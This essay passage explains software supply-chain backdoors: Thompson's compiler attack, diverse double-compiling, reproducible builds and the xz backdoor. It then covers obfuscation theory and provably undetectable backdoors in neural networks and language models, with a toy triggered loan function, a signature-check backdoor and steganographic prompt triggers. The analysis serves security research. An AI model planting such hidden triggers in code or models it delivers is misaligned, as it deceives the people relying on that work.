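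Thompson's moral was "You can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself." He warned that an attacker could use an assembler, a loader or the processor's microcode in the same way, and that lower levels would be harder to inspect. Cox built a version of Thompson's attack for the modern Go compiler, and it survived recompilation from clean source. Lecture notes from NYU describe Win32.Induc.A, a worm found in 2009 that attacked the Delphi compiler to insert code into the programs it compiled.

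### Checking a compiler with a second one

Thompson's attack succeeds if the victim has only one compiler, and the obvious defenses don't prevent it. Nobody can compare a large binary with its source by hand, and random test programs would almost never contain the text that triggers the malicious code. Switching to an interpreted language leaves the same risk in the interpreter, which somebody has to compile.

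Henry Spencer suggested a better method in a short online post in 1998. Wheeler named it diverse double-compiling, worked out the details and gave the first public demonstration. It needs the suspect binary A, the source s that supposedly produced it, and an independent compiler T:

1. Compile s with A, and check that the result is identical to A.
2. Compile s with T. Call the result B.
3. Compile s again, this time with B. Call the result C.
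4. Compare C with A, bit for bit.

The first step is only a control that confirms the tester can repeat the build. A tampered compiler also passes it, as the third row of the table shows.

B and A will contain different instructions because different compilers produced them. But if s really is the source of A, both are translations of the same program and must do the same job. Wheeler's later dissertation compares this to compiling a program that prints the sum of 2 and 2 with two C compilers. The two binaries differ, but each prints 4. In double-compiling, the program is itself a compiler, so its output is another binary. A and B must therefore turn the same source into the same binary, which means C should be identical to A. The suspect compiler isn't used to produce B or C, so any malicious code in it cannot affect them. With Thompson's compiler as the suspect, C would be the clean 10,724-byte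 version, which would not match the 12,918-byte original.

Wheeler's 2009 dissertation, *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, gives a formal proof of the method and applies it to four compilers, including GCC and a deliberately corrupted Lisp compiler. It also covers the common case in which an older version of the suspect compiler was used to build it. In that case, the tester first compiles the older version's source with the trusted compiler T, then uses the result to compile the newer source.

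For any of this to work, compilation has to be deterministic, so that the same source and settings always produce the same bits. In Cox's run, the first copy that the tampered compiler made of itself differed from the original in six bytes, because the compiler stores the source file's name in the binary. Another round of compilation removed the difference. Time stamps, random numbers and uninitialized memory can also cause mismatches, so a mismatch is a reason to investigate but doesn't prove sabotage. Wheeler's first test, which used a small C compiler called tcc with GCC as T, ran into ordinary problems with 8-bit values and high-precision constants.

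The second compiler must correctly handle the language features that the source uses, and it must not contain the same trojan. It can be slow, support only part of the language or contain a backdoor aimed at something else, as long as none of this affects how it compiles the source for this test. Wheeler recommends a compiler with a separate history, ideally one much older than the suspect, since an attacker would have had trouble planting a trojan for a compiler that did not yet exist. A compiler with a formal proof of correctness would also be a good choice. Cox points out that the tester need not know which of the two compilers is the suspicious one. If the results match, either both are clean or both contain the same backdoor.

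Somebody also has to review the source, because a match proves only that the binary corresponds to it. A backdoor visible in the source would pass, and so would the best entries in the Underhanded C Contest. Wheeler describes an attacker who adds self-copying code to the source of version 2 of a compiler and removes it from version 3. If version 2 compiled version 3, the newer binary may still contain the malicious code, although its source is clean. Wheeler advises repeating the double compilation for every release, or at least regularly.

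### Reproducible builds

Most programs are not compilers, and a single recompilation is enough to check them if the build is reproducible, meaning that anyone who uses the same source, tools and settings gets an identical binary. An attacker who breaks into a company's build server can alter the product without touching the source, but an outsider who rebuilds a reproducible program will see that the binaries differ. Cannon (2026), in *What's missing to have reproducible builds on PyPI*, cites the attack on the software company SolarWinds as evidence of this danger.

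Making a build reproducible takes work, because build tools tend to record the date, the folder or the user's name. In 2026 a user couldn't reproduce Arch Linux's package of the search tool grep, although Arch's own server reported success. The build downloads translations from a remote site, so its result can depend on when it runs.

Debian, one of the largest Linux distributions, made reproducibility a condition of release in May 2026. The Debian Release Team's *bits from the release team* (2026) announced that the team's software now blocks new packages that Debian's rebuilding service can't reproduce, and existing ones that stop being reproducible. *Reproductibilité obligatoire, tests de paquets binaires et nouvelle architecture* (Sibaud, 2026) reported that the service could reproduce 98.29 percent of the processor-independent packages in Debian's next version. Some packages may get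 exceptions, according to Reproducible Builds (2026), the project that coordinates this work.

According to the project, Debian developers used to build each package twice in a test system and compare the results. This showed whether a package could be reproducible, but not whether the copy that users download was built from the published source. If an attacker had compromised the official build machine, the two test builds would still have matched. Debian's new service tries to reproduce the official packages, so it can expose such an attack.

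Other software is further behind. IzzyOnDroid, a collection of Android apps, reached reproducible builds for two thirds of its apps in June 2026 (Reproducible Builds, 2026). In October 2025, Reproducible Builds (2025) reported that Google's Play Store broke reproducible builds for the messaging app Signal. Python's main package index still had no defined way to do reproducible builds in August 2026, though Cannon thinks it could introduce one without extra work for people who upload packages.

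Even if every rebuild of a program matched, that would not rule out Thompson's attack, because everyone who used the same tampered compiler would get the same tampered binary.

### Building from a tiny seed

Double-compiling closes this gap for one compiler at a time. Another approach, called bootstrappable builds, avoids existing compiler binaries and builds everything from a seed, a binary small enough for a person to check every byte. The seed builds a slightly more capable tool from source, that tool builds a simple compiler, and the chain continues up to a full compiler such as GCC. According to a commenter on Hacker News, the seed for the Linux distribution Guix is 357 bytes, plus a ready-made library. The 357 bytes take up 714 characters in hexadecimal, or about ten lines of text.

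Anyone can also build the current version of Go through a chain of compilers, starting with Go 1.4, whose compiler is written in C, and using each version to compile the next. Cox argues that a backdoor cannot hide in the binaries because the Go compiler never has to compile itself. However, the chain starts with a C compiler, and a backdoor there could in principle affect every compiler built after it.

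Few distributions have adopted bootstrappable builds, as one commenter on Hacker News regretted. A contributor to a distribution called stagex wrote there (2026) that in 2025 it had become the first to build everything reproducibly from source in this way, and that it requires several maintainers to rebuild and sign the results on their own hardware. A builder still has to trust the processor that the seed runs on and, usually, an operating system. Wheeler's answer to the same problem in double-compiling is to treat all the software on a machine as the suspect binary and rebuild it on a different kind of machine.

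### The xz backdoor

Cox wrote in October 2023 that nobody needs Thompson's backdoor, because there are far easier ways to attack software on its way to users. One such attack, on the compression program xz, was already under way. Many other programs load xz's library, liblzma, and Lasse Collin maintained the project as an unpaid hobby. Starting in October 2021, someone using the name Jia Tan sent in useful changes, one of which fixed an apparent problem with reproducible builds. Other accounts, probably fake, complained that Collin was slow and pressed for a new maintainer. Cox's *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (research!rsc, 2024) shows that Jia Tan could change the project's code directly by the end of 2022 and published a first release in March 2023.

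In February 2024 Jia Tan added compiled malicious code to the project's public repository, scrambled inside files that looked like test data. A compression library needs damaged and unusual files for testing. According to an old note in the same folder, many of the test files had no better "source code" than the files themselves because they were made by hand, so reviewers would not have expected to be able to read them.

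The code that unpacked these files was in a build script that Jia Tan added only to the release archive, the bundle that Linux distributions download and compile, not to the repository. Maintainers routinely add standard scripts to such archives, so an extra one didn't look suspicious, but Jia Tan had altered this one. Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, describes how the altered script extracted a second script from one of the test files. The second script added the malicious code to the library only if it was running on the right kind of Linux machine, with GCC, as part of a Debian or RPM package build, so an investigator who compiled xz by hand would probably have got a clean copy.

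The backdoor targeted OpenSSH, which administrators use to log in to servers remotely. OpenSSH doesn't use liblzma directly, but Debian and several other distributions modify it to work with the system manager systemd, whose library loads liblzma. Once loaded, the backdoor replaced a function that OpenSSH uses to check RSA keys. According to Cox, the attacker could then run any command on the server without logging in, by hiding it at the start of a connection.

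Andres Freund, who said he was not a security researcher, traced slow logins on machines running Debian's development version to xz. A failed login took 0.807 seconds instead of 0.299 because the backdoor was searching memory for the functions it needed. The memory checker Valgrind also reported errors. Jia Tan had already released a new version that dealt with these errors, and had said the test files were replaced to make them easier to reproduce. Freund alerted Debian and other distributions privately on March 28, 2024, and published his findings the next day.

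By then, the backdoored versions had been spreading for almost five weeks. They had reached Debian's unstable and testing branches, Fedora's development branch and the beta of Fedora 40, but Freund found that few finished releases included them. On the day he raised the alarm, Jia Tan was asking Ubuntu to adopt the latest version. The attack might have failed anyway, because systemd's developers had accepted a change in early March that stopped its library from loading liblzma. Cox reports speculation that this change made the attacker hurry.

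Rebuilding the packages from the release archive would not have exposed the backdoor, because the archive already contained the altered script and every rebuild would have produced the same backdoored library. Comparing the archive with the repository could have revealed the script, and Arch Linux switched to building xz from the repository on the day of Freund's warning. But the malicious code was also in the repository, in files that nobody could read. Checking that a binary matches its source protects people only if the source includes everything the build uses and a person can review all of it.

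When those conditions hold, a given source, compiler and settings can produce only one correct binary. A difference of even one bit shows that something is wrong, however well the backdoor is hidden, and whoever finds the difference doesn't need to know the trigger or understand the attack. Checking that a provider trained a neural network as claimed is much harder. When a language model turns a description into code, there is no single correct output to compare the code with.

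## What obfuscation theory says a program can hide

A reviewer with no correct output for comparison has to judge a program by what it does. Nobody can build the ideal tool for this, which would take any program and the bank's loan rule and report whether the program ever approves a loan that the rule forbids. In 1951 Henry Gordon Rice proved that no algorithm can decide a nontrivial property of behavior correctly for every program. A property is nontrivial if some programs have it and others don't, and it concerns behavior if it depends only on what a program does, not on how it is written.

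### Why Rice's theorem is weaker than it sounds

The theorem follows from the halting problem. Alan Turing had shown that no algorithm can tell, for every program, whether it will eventually stop. Suppose our contractor changes the loan program so that, when given one secret reference number, it runs an unrelated program P and approves the loan once P finishes. If P runs forever, the loan program never answers on that input, so the backdoor works only if P stops. A tool that recognized every working backdoor and raised no false alarms would therefore solve the halting problem.

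But a reviewer doesn't have to be right about every program. Anyone who found P inside a loan rule would send the code back without asking whether P stops. Compilers for strictly typed languages similarly reject every program they can't show to be free of type errors, including some that would have run correctly. Honest authors sometimes have to rewrite harmless code as a result, but rewriting a two-line rule takes little work.

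The theorem also doesn't cover programs that have a fixed input size and no loops, such as the loan program if every amount fits in 64 bits. Computer scientists model these programs as Boolean circuits, which are networks of AND, OR and NOT gates. A tester could in principle run a circuit on every input, but the reference number alone has 2^128 possible values, and nobody knows a method that is fast for all circuits. Reading the circuit might give the bank a shortcut over running it, and obfuscation is the attempt to prevent that.

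### The ideal of a black box

An obfuscator takes a program and returns another that does the same thing but is hard to understand. In *On the (Im)possibility of Obfuscating Programs* (2001), Barak, Goldreich and colleagues defined an ideal obfuscator. Its output computes the same function as the original program, is at most polynomially larger, and is a "virtual black box", meaning that whatever someone can efficiently work out from the obfuscated code, they could also have worked out by running the program on inputs of their choice.

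To make this precise, let O(C) be the obfuscated version of a circuit C, and let A be any efficient algorithm that reads O(C) and answers yes or no. There must then be an efficient algorithm S that knows only the size of C and can run it, but can't read it, and that answers yes with almost the same probability:

|Pr[A(O(C)) = yes] − Pr[S, running C, = yes]| ≤ a negligible amount

With an obfuscator like this, someone who discovered a fast way to factor large numbers could sell a code-breaking program that used the method without revealing it. The contractor could also obfuscate the loan program whose code visibly contains the secret reference number. The bank would then learn no more from reading the obfuscated program than from testing it.

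Barak and colleagues proved that no obfuscator can do this for every program. Their proof relies on something that a person who holds a program's code can do and a tester can't, which is to give the code to another program as input. Take two random secret strings, α and β, each k bits long, and write two programs:

- The lock returns β if its input is α, and zeros for any other input.
- The checker takes a program as its input, runs that program on α, and returns 1 if the answer is β and 0 otherwise.

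A tester who can only run these programs will see only zeros, because getting any other output requires guessing α for the lock or giving the checker a program that already answers α with β. The tester therefore can't tell the lock from an empty program that always returns zeros. Someone who has the code, however scrambled, can give the lock's code to the checker and get a 1, whereas the empty program would produce a 0. The code therefore always reveals one bit that running the programs does not. Combining the lock and the checker into one program, with an input that selects which of them runs, extends the result to single programs.

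The argument needs an extra step for circuits, because a circuit accepts inputs of only one length and the obfuscated lock may be too long for the checker. Barak and colleagues redesigned the checker to output α in encrypted form and to perform logical operations on encrypted bits. A reader can then evaluate the lock gate by gate without learning α, and use the checker to test whether the final result is an encryption of β.

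The lock and checker, which Barak and colleagues admit are "somewhat contrived", rule out an obfuscator that works on every program, but a contractor needs to hide only one check in one program. The same paper shows that obfuscation can also fail for more ordinary kinds of program. It constructs digital signature schemes that are secure in normal use, but whose secret key anyone can extract from any program that signs with it.

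### Indistinguishability obfuscation

Because the ideal was unachievable, Barak and colleagues proposed weaker goals. One of them, indistinguishability obfuscation (iO), has since become a central tool of cryptography. It requires that if two circuits have the same size and give the same output on every input, no efficient algorithm can tell their obfuscated versions apart.

For example, one programmer might write the loan rule as `amount <= 4 * (income - debts)` and another as `amount + 4 * debts <= 4 * income`. The two agree as long as the numbers are small enough not to overflow. If someone pads the shorter one to the length of the longer and obfuscates one of them, nobody can tell which it was. A very slow obfuscator could achieve this by searching through all programs of the given size in alphabetical order and returning the first that behaves like the original, so both versions of the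 rule would produce the same text. It is hard to get a similar effect in a reasonable time.

This guarantee doesn't promise to hide anything in particular, but it is as good as any other method of obfuscation, apart from the extra size. Suppose another method hides a secret in program f by turning it into program g. Since f and g behave identically, their iO versions look alike once f has been padded to the size of g. Anyone who could extract the secret from the iO version of f could therefore extract it from the iO version of g. They could then get the secret from g by applying iO to it themselves, which means the other method didn't hide it.

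For years, every proposed construction of iO relied on a hardness assumption that its designers had invented for the purpose, and other cryptographers broke several of them. Jain, Lin and Sahai (2020), in *Indistinguishability Obfuscation from Well-Founded Assumptions*, gave the first construction that rests on older and better-studied assumptions. There are four:

- **Learning with errors.** Someone takes many linear equations in the same secret numbers and adds a small random error to each answer. No efficient algorithm can tell the answers from random numbers.
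- **Learning parity with noise, over large fields.** Here most of the answers are exact, but a small random share of them are completely random. Again, they look random as a whole.
- **A very simple pseudorandom generator.** Each bit of its output depends on only a fixed number of bits of the seed, yet it stretches n bits to n^(1+τ) for some τ above zero.
- **SXDH.** This concerns pairs of algebraic groups that are linked by a special map. In either group, someone who sees g^x and g^y can't tell g^(xy) from g^z, where z is random.

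The construction needs these problems to resist even attackers whose running time grows faster than any polynomial. Jain and colleagues point out that cryptographers introduced all four for purposes unrelated to iO. The problem behind learning parity with noise dates back to coding theory in the 1950s, and researchers have made little progress since then on solving it efficiently.

iO still has weaker foundations than everyday encryption. *Separating Quantum Indistinguishability Obfuscation from Falsifiable Assumptions* (Barhoush, Morimae and Movassagh, 2026), which reviews the field as of August 2026, notes that quantum computers would break the SXDH assumption. Nobody has a quantum-resistant construction from well-studied assumptions, and several of the newer assumptions proposed for one have already been broken. The paper also cites a proof by Goldwasser and Rothblum that iO for all circuits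 can't be statistically secure unless a widely held belief in complexity theory is false. If that belief is true, a reader with unlimited computing power could defeat the obfuscation. The backdoor that Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa plant in a network's weights is statistically undetectable, so even that reader couldn't detect it.

Bogdanov and colleagues describe the existing constructions of iO as "concretely inefficient" and far from practical. No contractor could deliver a loan program obfuscated this way today, so the following result is about what is possible in principle.

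### How to hide a trigger completely

Kalavasis, Sotiraki and colleagues (2024), in *Injecting Undetectable Backdoors in Obfuscated Neural Networks and Language Models*, combined iO with a pseudorandom generator to plant a backdoor that no efficient reader can detect. The idea already works for the loan program. Let G be a pseudorandom generator that stretches 128 bits to 256. The contractor chooses a secret 128-bit string s, calculates Y = G(s), and writes only Y into the program:

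```
def approve(income, debts, amount, reference):
    if G(reference) == Y:
        return True
    return amount <= 4 * (income - debts)
```

An application with the reference number s always succeeds. The code doesn't reveal s, but a reviewer would ask why a loan program needs a pseudorandom generator, so the contractor obfuscates the program with iO before delivering it. Can the bank tell the result from an obfuscated copy of the honest program?

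The definition of iO covers only programs that always behave identically, and these two differ when the reference number is s. The proof therefore uses a third program, which we'll call the dud. It has the same lines as the backdoored program, but its Y is a truly random 256-bit string.

| Program | Stored number Y | Does a trigger exist? |
|---|---|---|
| Honest | none | No |
| Dud | random 256-bit string | No, except with probability at most 2^-128 |
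| Backdoored | G(s) | Yes, the number s |

**The honest program and the dud look alike.** G has at most 2^128 different outputs, one for each seed, but there are 2^256 strings of 256 bits. The chance that a random Y is one of G's outputs is therefore at most 2^128 / 2^256 = 2^-128. Otherwise, no reference number can pass the check, so the dud behaves exactly like the honest program. Once the honest program is padded with idle instructions to match the dud's size, iO guarantees that no efficient distinguisher can tell the obfuscated versions apart.

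**No efficient algorithm can tell the obfuscated dud from the obfuscated backdoored program.** The two programs differ only in whether Y is random or came from the generator G. If an efficient distinguisher could tell their obfuscated versions apart, anyone could use it to break G. They would write a 256-bit string of unknown origin into the program as Y, obfuscate the program and run the distinguisher on the result. The output would show whether the string was random or came from G. No efficient algorithm can do that, so the distinguisher can't exist.

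Putting the two halves together, the honest and backdoored programs also look alike after obfuscation. For any efficient distinguisher A,

|Pr[A(O(honest)) = yes] − Pr[A(O(backdoored)) = yes]| ≤ ε_iO + 2^-128 + ε_G

where ε_iO is the largest advantage that an efficient algorithm can have against the obfuscator, and ε_G is the largest it can have against the generator. Both are negligible under the assumptions.

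The bank can therefore have the complete code and still have no feasible way to tell whether it contains a backdoor. Even a future language model that analyzes code far better than any person is still an efficient algorithm, so the proof applies to it too unless it can break one of the underlying assumptions.

The check has to use something like a pseudorandom generator, because an ordinary hard puzzle wouldn't be enough. Kalavasis and colleagues consider a version in which the trigger is the solution to a logical formula. The backdoored program would contain a formula that has a solution, and its harmless counterpart would contain one that has none. Researchers believe no efficient algorithm can tell, for every formula, whether it has a solution. But for any particular solvable formula, a trivial algorithm can have the solution written into it. The contractor needs a way to produce puzzles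 that are hard on average, which a pseudorandom generator provides.

### Neural networks and language models

To apply this to a neural network, Kalavasis and colleagues assume that even an honest provider obfuscates its models before releasing them. The provider trains the network by any method, converts it into a Boolean circuit, obfuscates the circuit with iO and converts the result back into a network. A dishonest provider follows the same steps but adds the secret check just before obfuscating the circuit.

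The trigger changes only the last binary digits of the input numbers, so their values barely change. A digital signature in the same digits stops a bank that has caught one doctored application from producing another. If the assumptions hold, the backdoor is white-box undetectable, meaning that no efficient algorithm can detect it, even given all the weights.

Converting the circuit back into a network is awkward because a standard network's output changes continuously with its input. The network therefore can't turn every number exactly into binary digits, and it makes errors near the points where a digit flips. For an input of n numbers, the construction runs the circuit on 2n + 1 slightly shifted copies of the input. At most n − 1 of the copies can fall too close to such a point, so the median of the results is reliable.

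A language model takes text as input, so the secret that triggers a backdoor can't be hidden in the last digits of numerical inputs. Kalavasis and colleagues instead assume that it can be hidden in the text by steganography. They give the example of a list of commonly misspelled words, where the correct spelling stands for 0 and the common typo for 1. A prompt would need 128 of these words to carry a 128-bit secret. The delivered system contains two complete models, one honest and one malicious, and the secret switches from the first to the second. They leave open how to stop someone who has seen one triggered prompt from making more.

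Kalavasis and colleagues concede that simple precautions would defeat these triggers. A bank could add a little noise to every number, or have another language model correct the spelling of each prompt. They expect attackers to design triggers that survive these precautions.

Their theorem is compatible with an earlier remark by Goldwasser and colleagues, who wrote in 2022 that the guarantees of iO "are not strong enough to yield white-box undetectability", because that remark was about using obfuscation naively. If a provider obfuscates a classifier that accepts signed inputs, it still behaves differently from the honest one on every validly signed input, so the definition of iO doesn't guarantee that the two obfuscated classifiers are indistinguishable. Kalavasis and colleagues solve this by comparing each of them with a dud, a classifier whose backdoor no input can trigger. They also address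 a different question, since Goldwasser and colleagues had asked about natural training procedures, and nobody uses training followed by iO.

### Refusing code that nobody can read

The second change is the weak point of the result. In this proof, every program that counts as honest is itself obfuscated. Bogdanov and colleagues object that the honest models are contrived because they have to contain obfuscated circuits.

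A bank that normally receives two readable lines of code will notice if it gets an enormous, unreadable circuit of logic gates instead. It can't tell whether the circuit contains a backdoor, but it can refuse the delivery because the circuit is unreadable. The proof doesn't protect the contractor from that refusal.

Kalavasis and colleagues reply that honest companies have good reasons to obfuscate. A model's weights can reveal trade secrets or parts of its training data, and Microsoft already sells Office as compiled code without the source. The Office example shows that customers accept software they can't read, but ordinary compiled code has no guarantee like iO's, so the theorem doesn't apply to it. The definition of iO also covers only circuits of equal size, so an honest provider of a language model would have to pad its product to the size of two models, which it seems to have little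 reason to do.

For source code, then, the objection seems decisive when the buyer can insist on readable code. It is weaker if legitimate programs of the same kind already contain long numbers that nobody can explain, because a reviewer can't reject every program that has them.

### Everyday obfuscators

The obfuscators people use in practice have little in common with iO. Software companies use them to protect their products from copying, and criminals use them to hide malware. These tools rename variables, add code that never runs, and replace simple instructions with complicated equivalents. One popular technique, control-flow flattening, splits a function into pieces and puts them inside one loop, where a variable determines which piece runs next. Another is the opaque predicate, a condition whose outcome is fixed but not obvious. For example, x(x + 1) is even for every whole number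 x, so a branch for the odd case never runs and can be filled with misleading code.

None of these techniques comes with a proof that undoing it is hard. A hidden check remains somewhere in the code, and a sufficiently patient reader can find it. Language models can read code this thoroughly, and several studies from 2026 measured how well they handle these techniques.

*Robustness and Trade-offs for Code LLMs on Protected Code* (Wen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) tested seven models on translating or completing programs in four languages, obfuscated by five methods. The stronger models, such as GPT-4.1, translated about 90 percent of the obfuscated programs correctly on the first attempt. Cleaning up the code beforehand often didn't help.

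Compiled programs are harder to deobfuscate because compilation removes most of the names and structure. *Can LLMs Deobfuscate Binary Code?* (2026) tested how well nine models could restore readable code, using a collection of about 2.1 million obfuscated programs generated from 2,092 originals. Under severe obfuscation, the reasoning model DeepSeek-R1 preserved 63 percent of the meaning by the benchmark's own measure, compared with 58 percent for a model specially trained to undo obfuscation. On real malware, reasoning models reduced the code's complexity by nearly 60 percent.

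Models still struggle with code that has been obfuscated in several layers. In *Analyzing Chain of Thought (CoT) Approaches in Control Flow Code Deobfuscation Tasks* (2026), models removed more opaque predicates when the prompt explained why a condition was always true or always false. They did worse as the number of false branches grew or when several obfuscation methods were combined, and all of them sometimes made things up. *Challenges and Future Directions in Agentic Reverse Engineering Systems* (2026) warns that unfamiliar techniques are particularly hard for AI agents, which rely on patterns seen in training. GPT-4.1 and DeepSeek-R1 both date from 2025, so current models probably do better than these figures suggest.

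Obfuscation can even remove a source of error. *Post-Hoc Attention Steering of Large Language Models for Robust Code Understanding* (2026) describes a model that had to predict the output of a short Java program containing a function called `binomialCoefficient`. The model applied the textbook formula for binomial coefficients instead of following the code, and it got the right answer because the name was accurate. Someone writing underhanded code could choose a misleading name, and an obfuscator that scrambled the names would remove the misleading cue.

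High scores on these tasks don't show that models can find backdoors. Wen and colleagues judged translations by running them, and ordinary tests almost never include a secret reference number. A model could leave the contractor's check out of its translation and still pass. To find the check, a reader has to account for every branch in the code, including those that seem to do nothing.

A bank rarely needs this kind of detective work, because whoever obfuscated a program started from a more readable version, and the bank can refuse to pay until it receives that version. It can't do the same with a neural network, because training produces nothing more readable than the weights, even when the developer is honest.

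## Network backdoors that no efficient test can detect

Since the weights of an honestly trained network are already unreadable, a dishonest provider doesn't need iO to hide a backdoor in them. Goldwasser and colleagues proved in 2022 that a provider can plant a backdoor in certain simple networks by tampering only with the random numbers that training starts from. The bank has no feasible way to tell such a network from an honestly trained one, even if it examines every weight. They also showed how to add a backdoor to any classifier, but that backdoor is undetectable only to testers who don't look inside the classifier.

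### What a proof of undetectability covers

The definition involves three algorithms:

- **Train** is the procedure the bank asked for. It takes training data and returns a classifier h, which answers +1 (approve) or −1 (reject) for any application x.
- **Backdoor** is what the dishonest provider runs instead. It takes the same data and returns a classifier h̃ together with a backdoor key.
- **Activate** takes an application x and the key, and returns an altered application x′. The two must lie within a fixed distance of each other, and the classifier must give them opposite answers, so h̃(x′) = −h̃(x).

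Train outputs the range of classifiers that an honest provider would produce. The backdoor is undetectable if no efficient distinguisher can tell Backdoor's output from Train's, whatever the training data. It is black-box undetectable if this holds for distinguishers that can only run the classifier on applications of their choice. White-box undetectability, which the iO construction achieved, is much stronger because the distinguisher also gets all the weights. Goldwasser and colleagues also define a weaker version of undetectability for a bank that sees only averages, such as the error rate on a set of test loans.

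An undetectable backdoor can't make the classifier less accurate, because a simple accuracy test would then distinguish the backdoored classifier from a clean one. For the same reason, applications that trigger the backdoor must be extremely rare among ordinary ones. The input must also be longer than the key length that security requires, so a form with four short fields is too short for such a backdoor, but a loan file with years of account history is long enough.

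Undetectability does not limit what people can learn once the provider starts using the backdoor. A bank, for example, might catch a few doctored applications and study them. Goldwasser and colleagues define a separate property, non-replicability, by comparing two attackers who lack the key. One has only the classifier, while the other can also submit any applications and get back altered versions that trigger the backdoor. Both try to produce a new pair of nearby applications that get opposite answers, and the second attacker may not reuse the altered applications it received. The backdoor is non-replicable if seeing the altered applications gives at most a negligible advantage.

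A simpler definition would require that nobody without the key can find any such pair. That might be impossible to satisfy, because many honest classifiers already change their answer after a small, well-chosen change to the input. Researchers call these altered inputs adversarial examples.

### A signature check beside the classifier

To backdoor an arbitrary classifier h, Snoogle generates the two keys of a digital signature scheme, keeps the secret one, and builds the public checking procedure into the network. It treats each application as a string of bits with three parts. Almost everything is in w, then comes a single bit y, and the rest is σ, which is as long as a signature. In a loan file, y and σ could be the least significant digits of old account balances. The backdoored classifier works like this:

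```
h̃(w, y, σ) = (−1)^y        if σ is a valid signature of (w, y)
             h(w, y, σ)     otherwise
```

Suppose a file has 10,000 bits, a signature has 512, and the honest classifier rejects the application. The applicant pays Snoogle for its profile-cleaning service, which does the following:

1. It sets y to 0, because (−1)^0 = +1 means approval.
2. It signs (w, 0) with the secret key, which gives 512 bits.
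3. It writes those bits into the last part of the file.

When the bank runs the classifier, the signature check succeeds and the classifier approves the loan. At most 513 bits have changed, and the income, debts and requested amount are the same as before. If a clerk then corrects a typing error in the income, the signature no longer matches, and the application goes to h, which rejects it.

A tester who wants to catch Snoogle needs an application on which h and h̃ differ. The two functions give the same answer whenever σ isn't a valid signature, so the tester would have to forge one, that is, produce a valid signature without the secret key. By definition, no efficient algorithm can do this reliably if the signature scheme is secure. Cryptographers can build secure signature schemes from any one-way function, so the theorem only has to assume that one-way functions exist.

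Reading the network reveals the signature check but doesn't help anyone forge a signature, because the network contains only the public key. This backdoor is therefore black-box undetectable but not white-box undetectable. Goldwasser and colleagues also describe a signature scheme whose check fits into four network layers, so adding it wouldn't deepen a classifier that already has at least four. They think the resulting network would look more natural, but they couldn't prove that the check would go unnoticed.

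The signature backdoor is non-replicable, meaning that Snoogle's signed applications don't help anyone else attack the classifier. Copying a signature from one application into another fails, because a signature is valid only for the w and y that Snoogle signed. An attacker also can't learn anything useful from a large collection of signed applications, because they could have made a similar collection themselves by generating new keys, putting the new public key into a copy of the network, and signing applications with the new secret key. Those applications would be just like Snoogle's apart from the key.

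The construction also means that no efficient program can reliably confirm, just by querying a classifier, that it has no adversarial examples. If a training procedure produced classifiers with none, such a program would pass them and fail their backdoored counterparts, in which Snoogle can reverse any answer with a small change to the input. The program would therefore distinguish honest classifiers from backdoored ones, which the theorem rules out. Goldwasser and colleagues extend the argument to programs that read the weights, but this requires a backdoor that is also white-box undetectable.

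### Tampering with nothing but the random numbers

Their main example of such a backdoor uses random Fourier features, a training method that Ali Rahimi and Benjamin Recht introduced in 2007. It produces a network with one hidden layer of m units, called features:

h(x) = sign( w₁ cos(2π(g₁·x + b₁)) + … + w_m cos(2π(g_m·x + b_m)) )

Here x is the application, written as a list of d numbers. Each g is a list of d random numbers drawn from a normal distribution with mean 0 and variance 1, and g·x means multiplying the two lists entry by entry and adding up the results. Each b is a random number between 0 and 1. Training chooses only the weights w and leaves the g's and b's fixed. It can use any method that finds a good weighted sum.

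Each feature places the application somewhere along a wave, and g·x + b gives its position in periods. Moving by a whole number of periods doesn't change the cosine, while moving by an extra half period reverses its sign. For example, a shift of 3.5 periods gives

cos(2π(t + 3.5)) = cos(2πt + 7π) = −cos(2πt)

Snoogle's key is a list k of d numbers, and Activate simply adds it to the application. This moves each feature by g·k periods, so Snoogle chooses every g to make g·k very close to a half-integer, such as 0.5, −1.5 or 3.5. A toy network with three features shows the effect:

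| Weight w | Position before | Cosine before | Shift g·k | Position after | Cosine after |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.2 | 0.10 | 0.81 | 3.5 | 3.60 | −0.81 |
| 0.5 | 0.30 | −0.31 | −1.5 | −1.20 | 0.31 |
| −0.6 | 0.85 | 0.59 | 0.5 | 1.35 | −0.59 |

Adding k changes the weighted sum from −0.35 to +0.35, so a rejection becomes an approval. Reversing the sign of every cosine reverses the sign of the sum whatever the weights are, so Snoogle doesn't need to tamper with how the weights are trained. The real shifts are only approximately half-integers, so the proof assumes the sum is never too close to zero. In an honest network, g·k could have any fractional part, and adding k would shift the features by unrelated amounts.

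Snoogle can get suitable g's by drawing them honestly and throwing away each one for which g·k isn't near a half-integer. Plotted as points in d-dimensional space, honest g's form a round cloud. The ones Snoogle keeps form a cloud of the same shape, cut into thin parallel layers at right angles to the key. Cryptographers call this distribution "Gaussian pancakes". Anyone who knows the key can project the points onto its direction and see the layers immediately. Without the key, they would have to find that one direction in a space with many dimensions.

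The evidence that this is hard comes from a problem called continuous learning with errors (CLWE), which Bruna, Regev and colleagues (2020), in *Continuous LWE*, introduced as a real-number version of learning with errors. The solver receives many pairs (y, z), where y is a list of bell-curve numbers. Either every z is a random number between 0 and 1, or every z is the fractional part of

γ(y·s) + e

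where s is a secret list of length 1, γ is a scale factor of at least 2√d, and e is a small random error. The solver has to work out which kind of pairs they received. Bruna and colleagues showed that an efficient method would lead to an efficient quantum algorithm for lattice problems that cryptographers believe to be hard, and *Continuous LWE is as Hard as LWE* (2022) showed the same without the need for a quantum computer.

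We can connect CLWE to the backdoor by keeping only the pairs whose z is close to 1/2. If the z's are random, the remaining y's are a random selection, so they still form a round cloud. If the z's follow the formula, the remaining y's lie in pancakes, with the key k equal to γs. Anyone who could tell pancakes from a round cloud could therefore solve CLWE.

A distinguisher that sees the whole trained network has no advantage either. Given a set of g's of unknown origin, anyone could train the weights on top of them and run the distinguisher on the finished network. If it could recognize backdoored networks, this test would also show whether the g's came from the pancake distribution.

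Goldwasser and colleagues also reduce the number of entries the key changes. They build pancakes in a small number of dimensions, scatter these among the application's entries and fill the rest with ordinary bell-curve numbers. For an application with 10,000 numbers, the key might change only 100 of them. But the proof then relies on CLWE being hard in 100 dimensions rather than 10,000, so changing fewer entries weakens the protection.

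Snoogle uses the bank's data and follows the bank's training procedure exactly. It could even give the bank a cryptographic proof that it did so. The bank can also ask to see the random numbers, which are in the network anyway and pass every efficient test.

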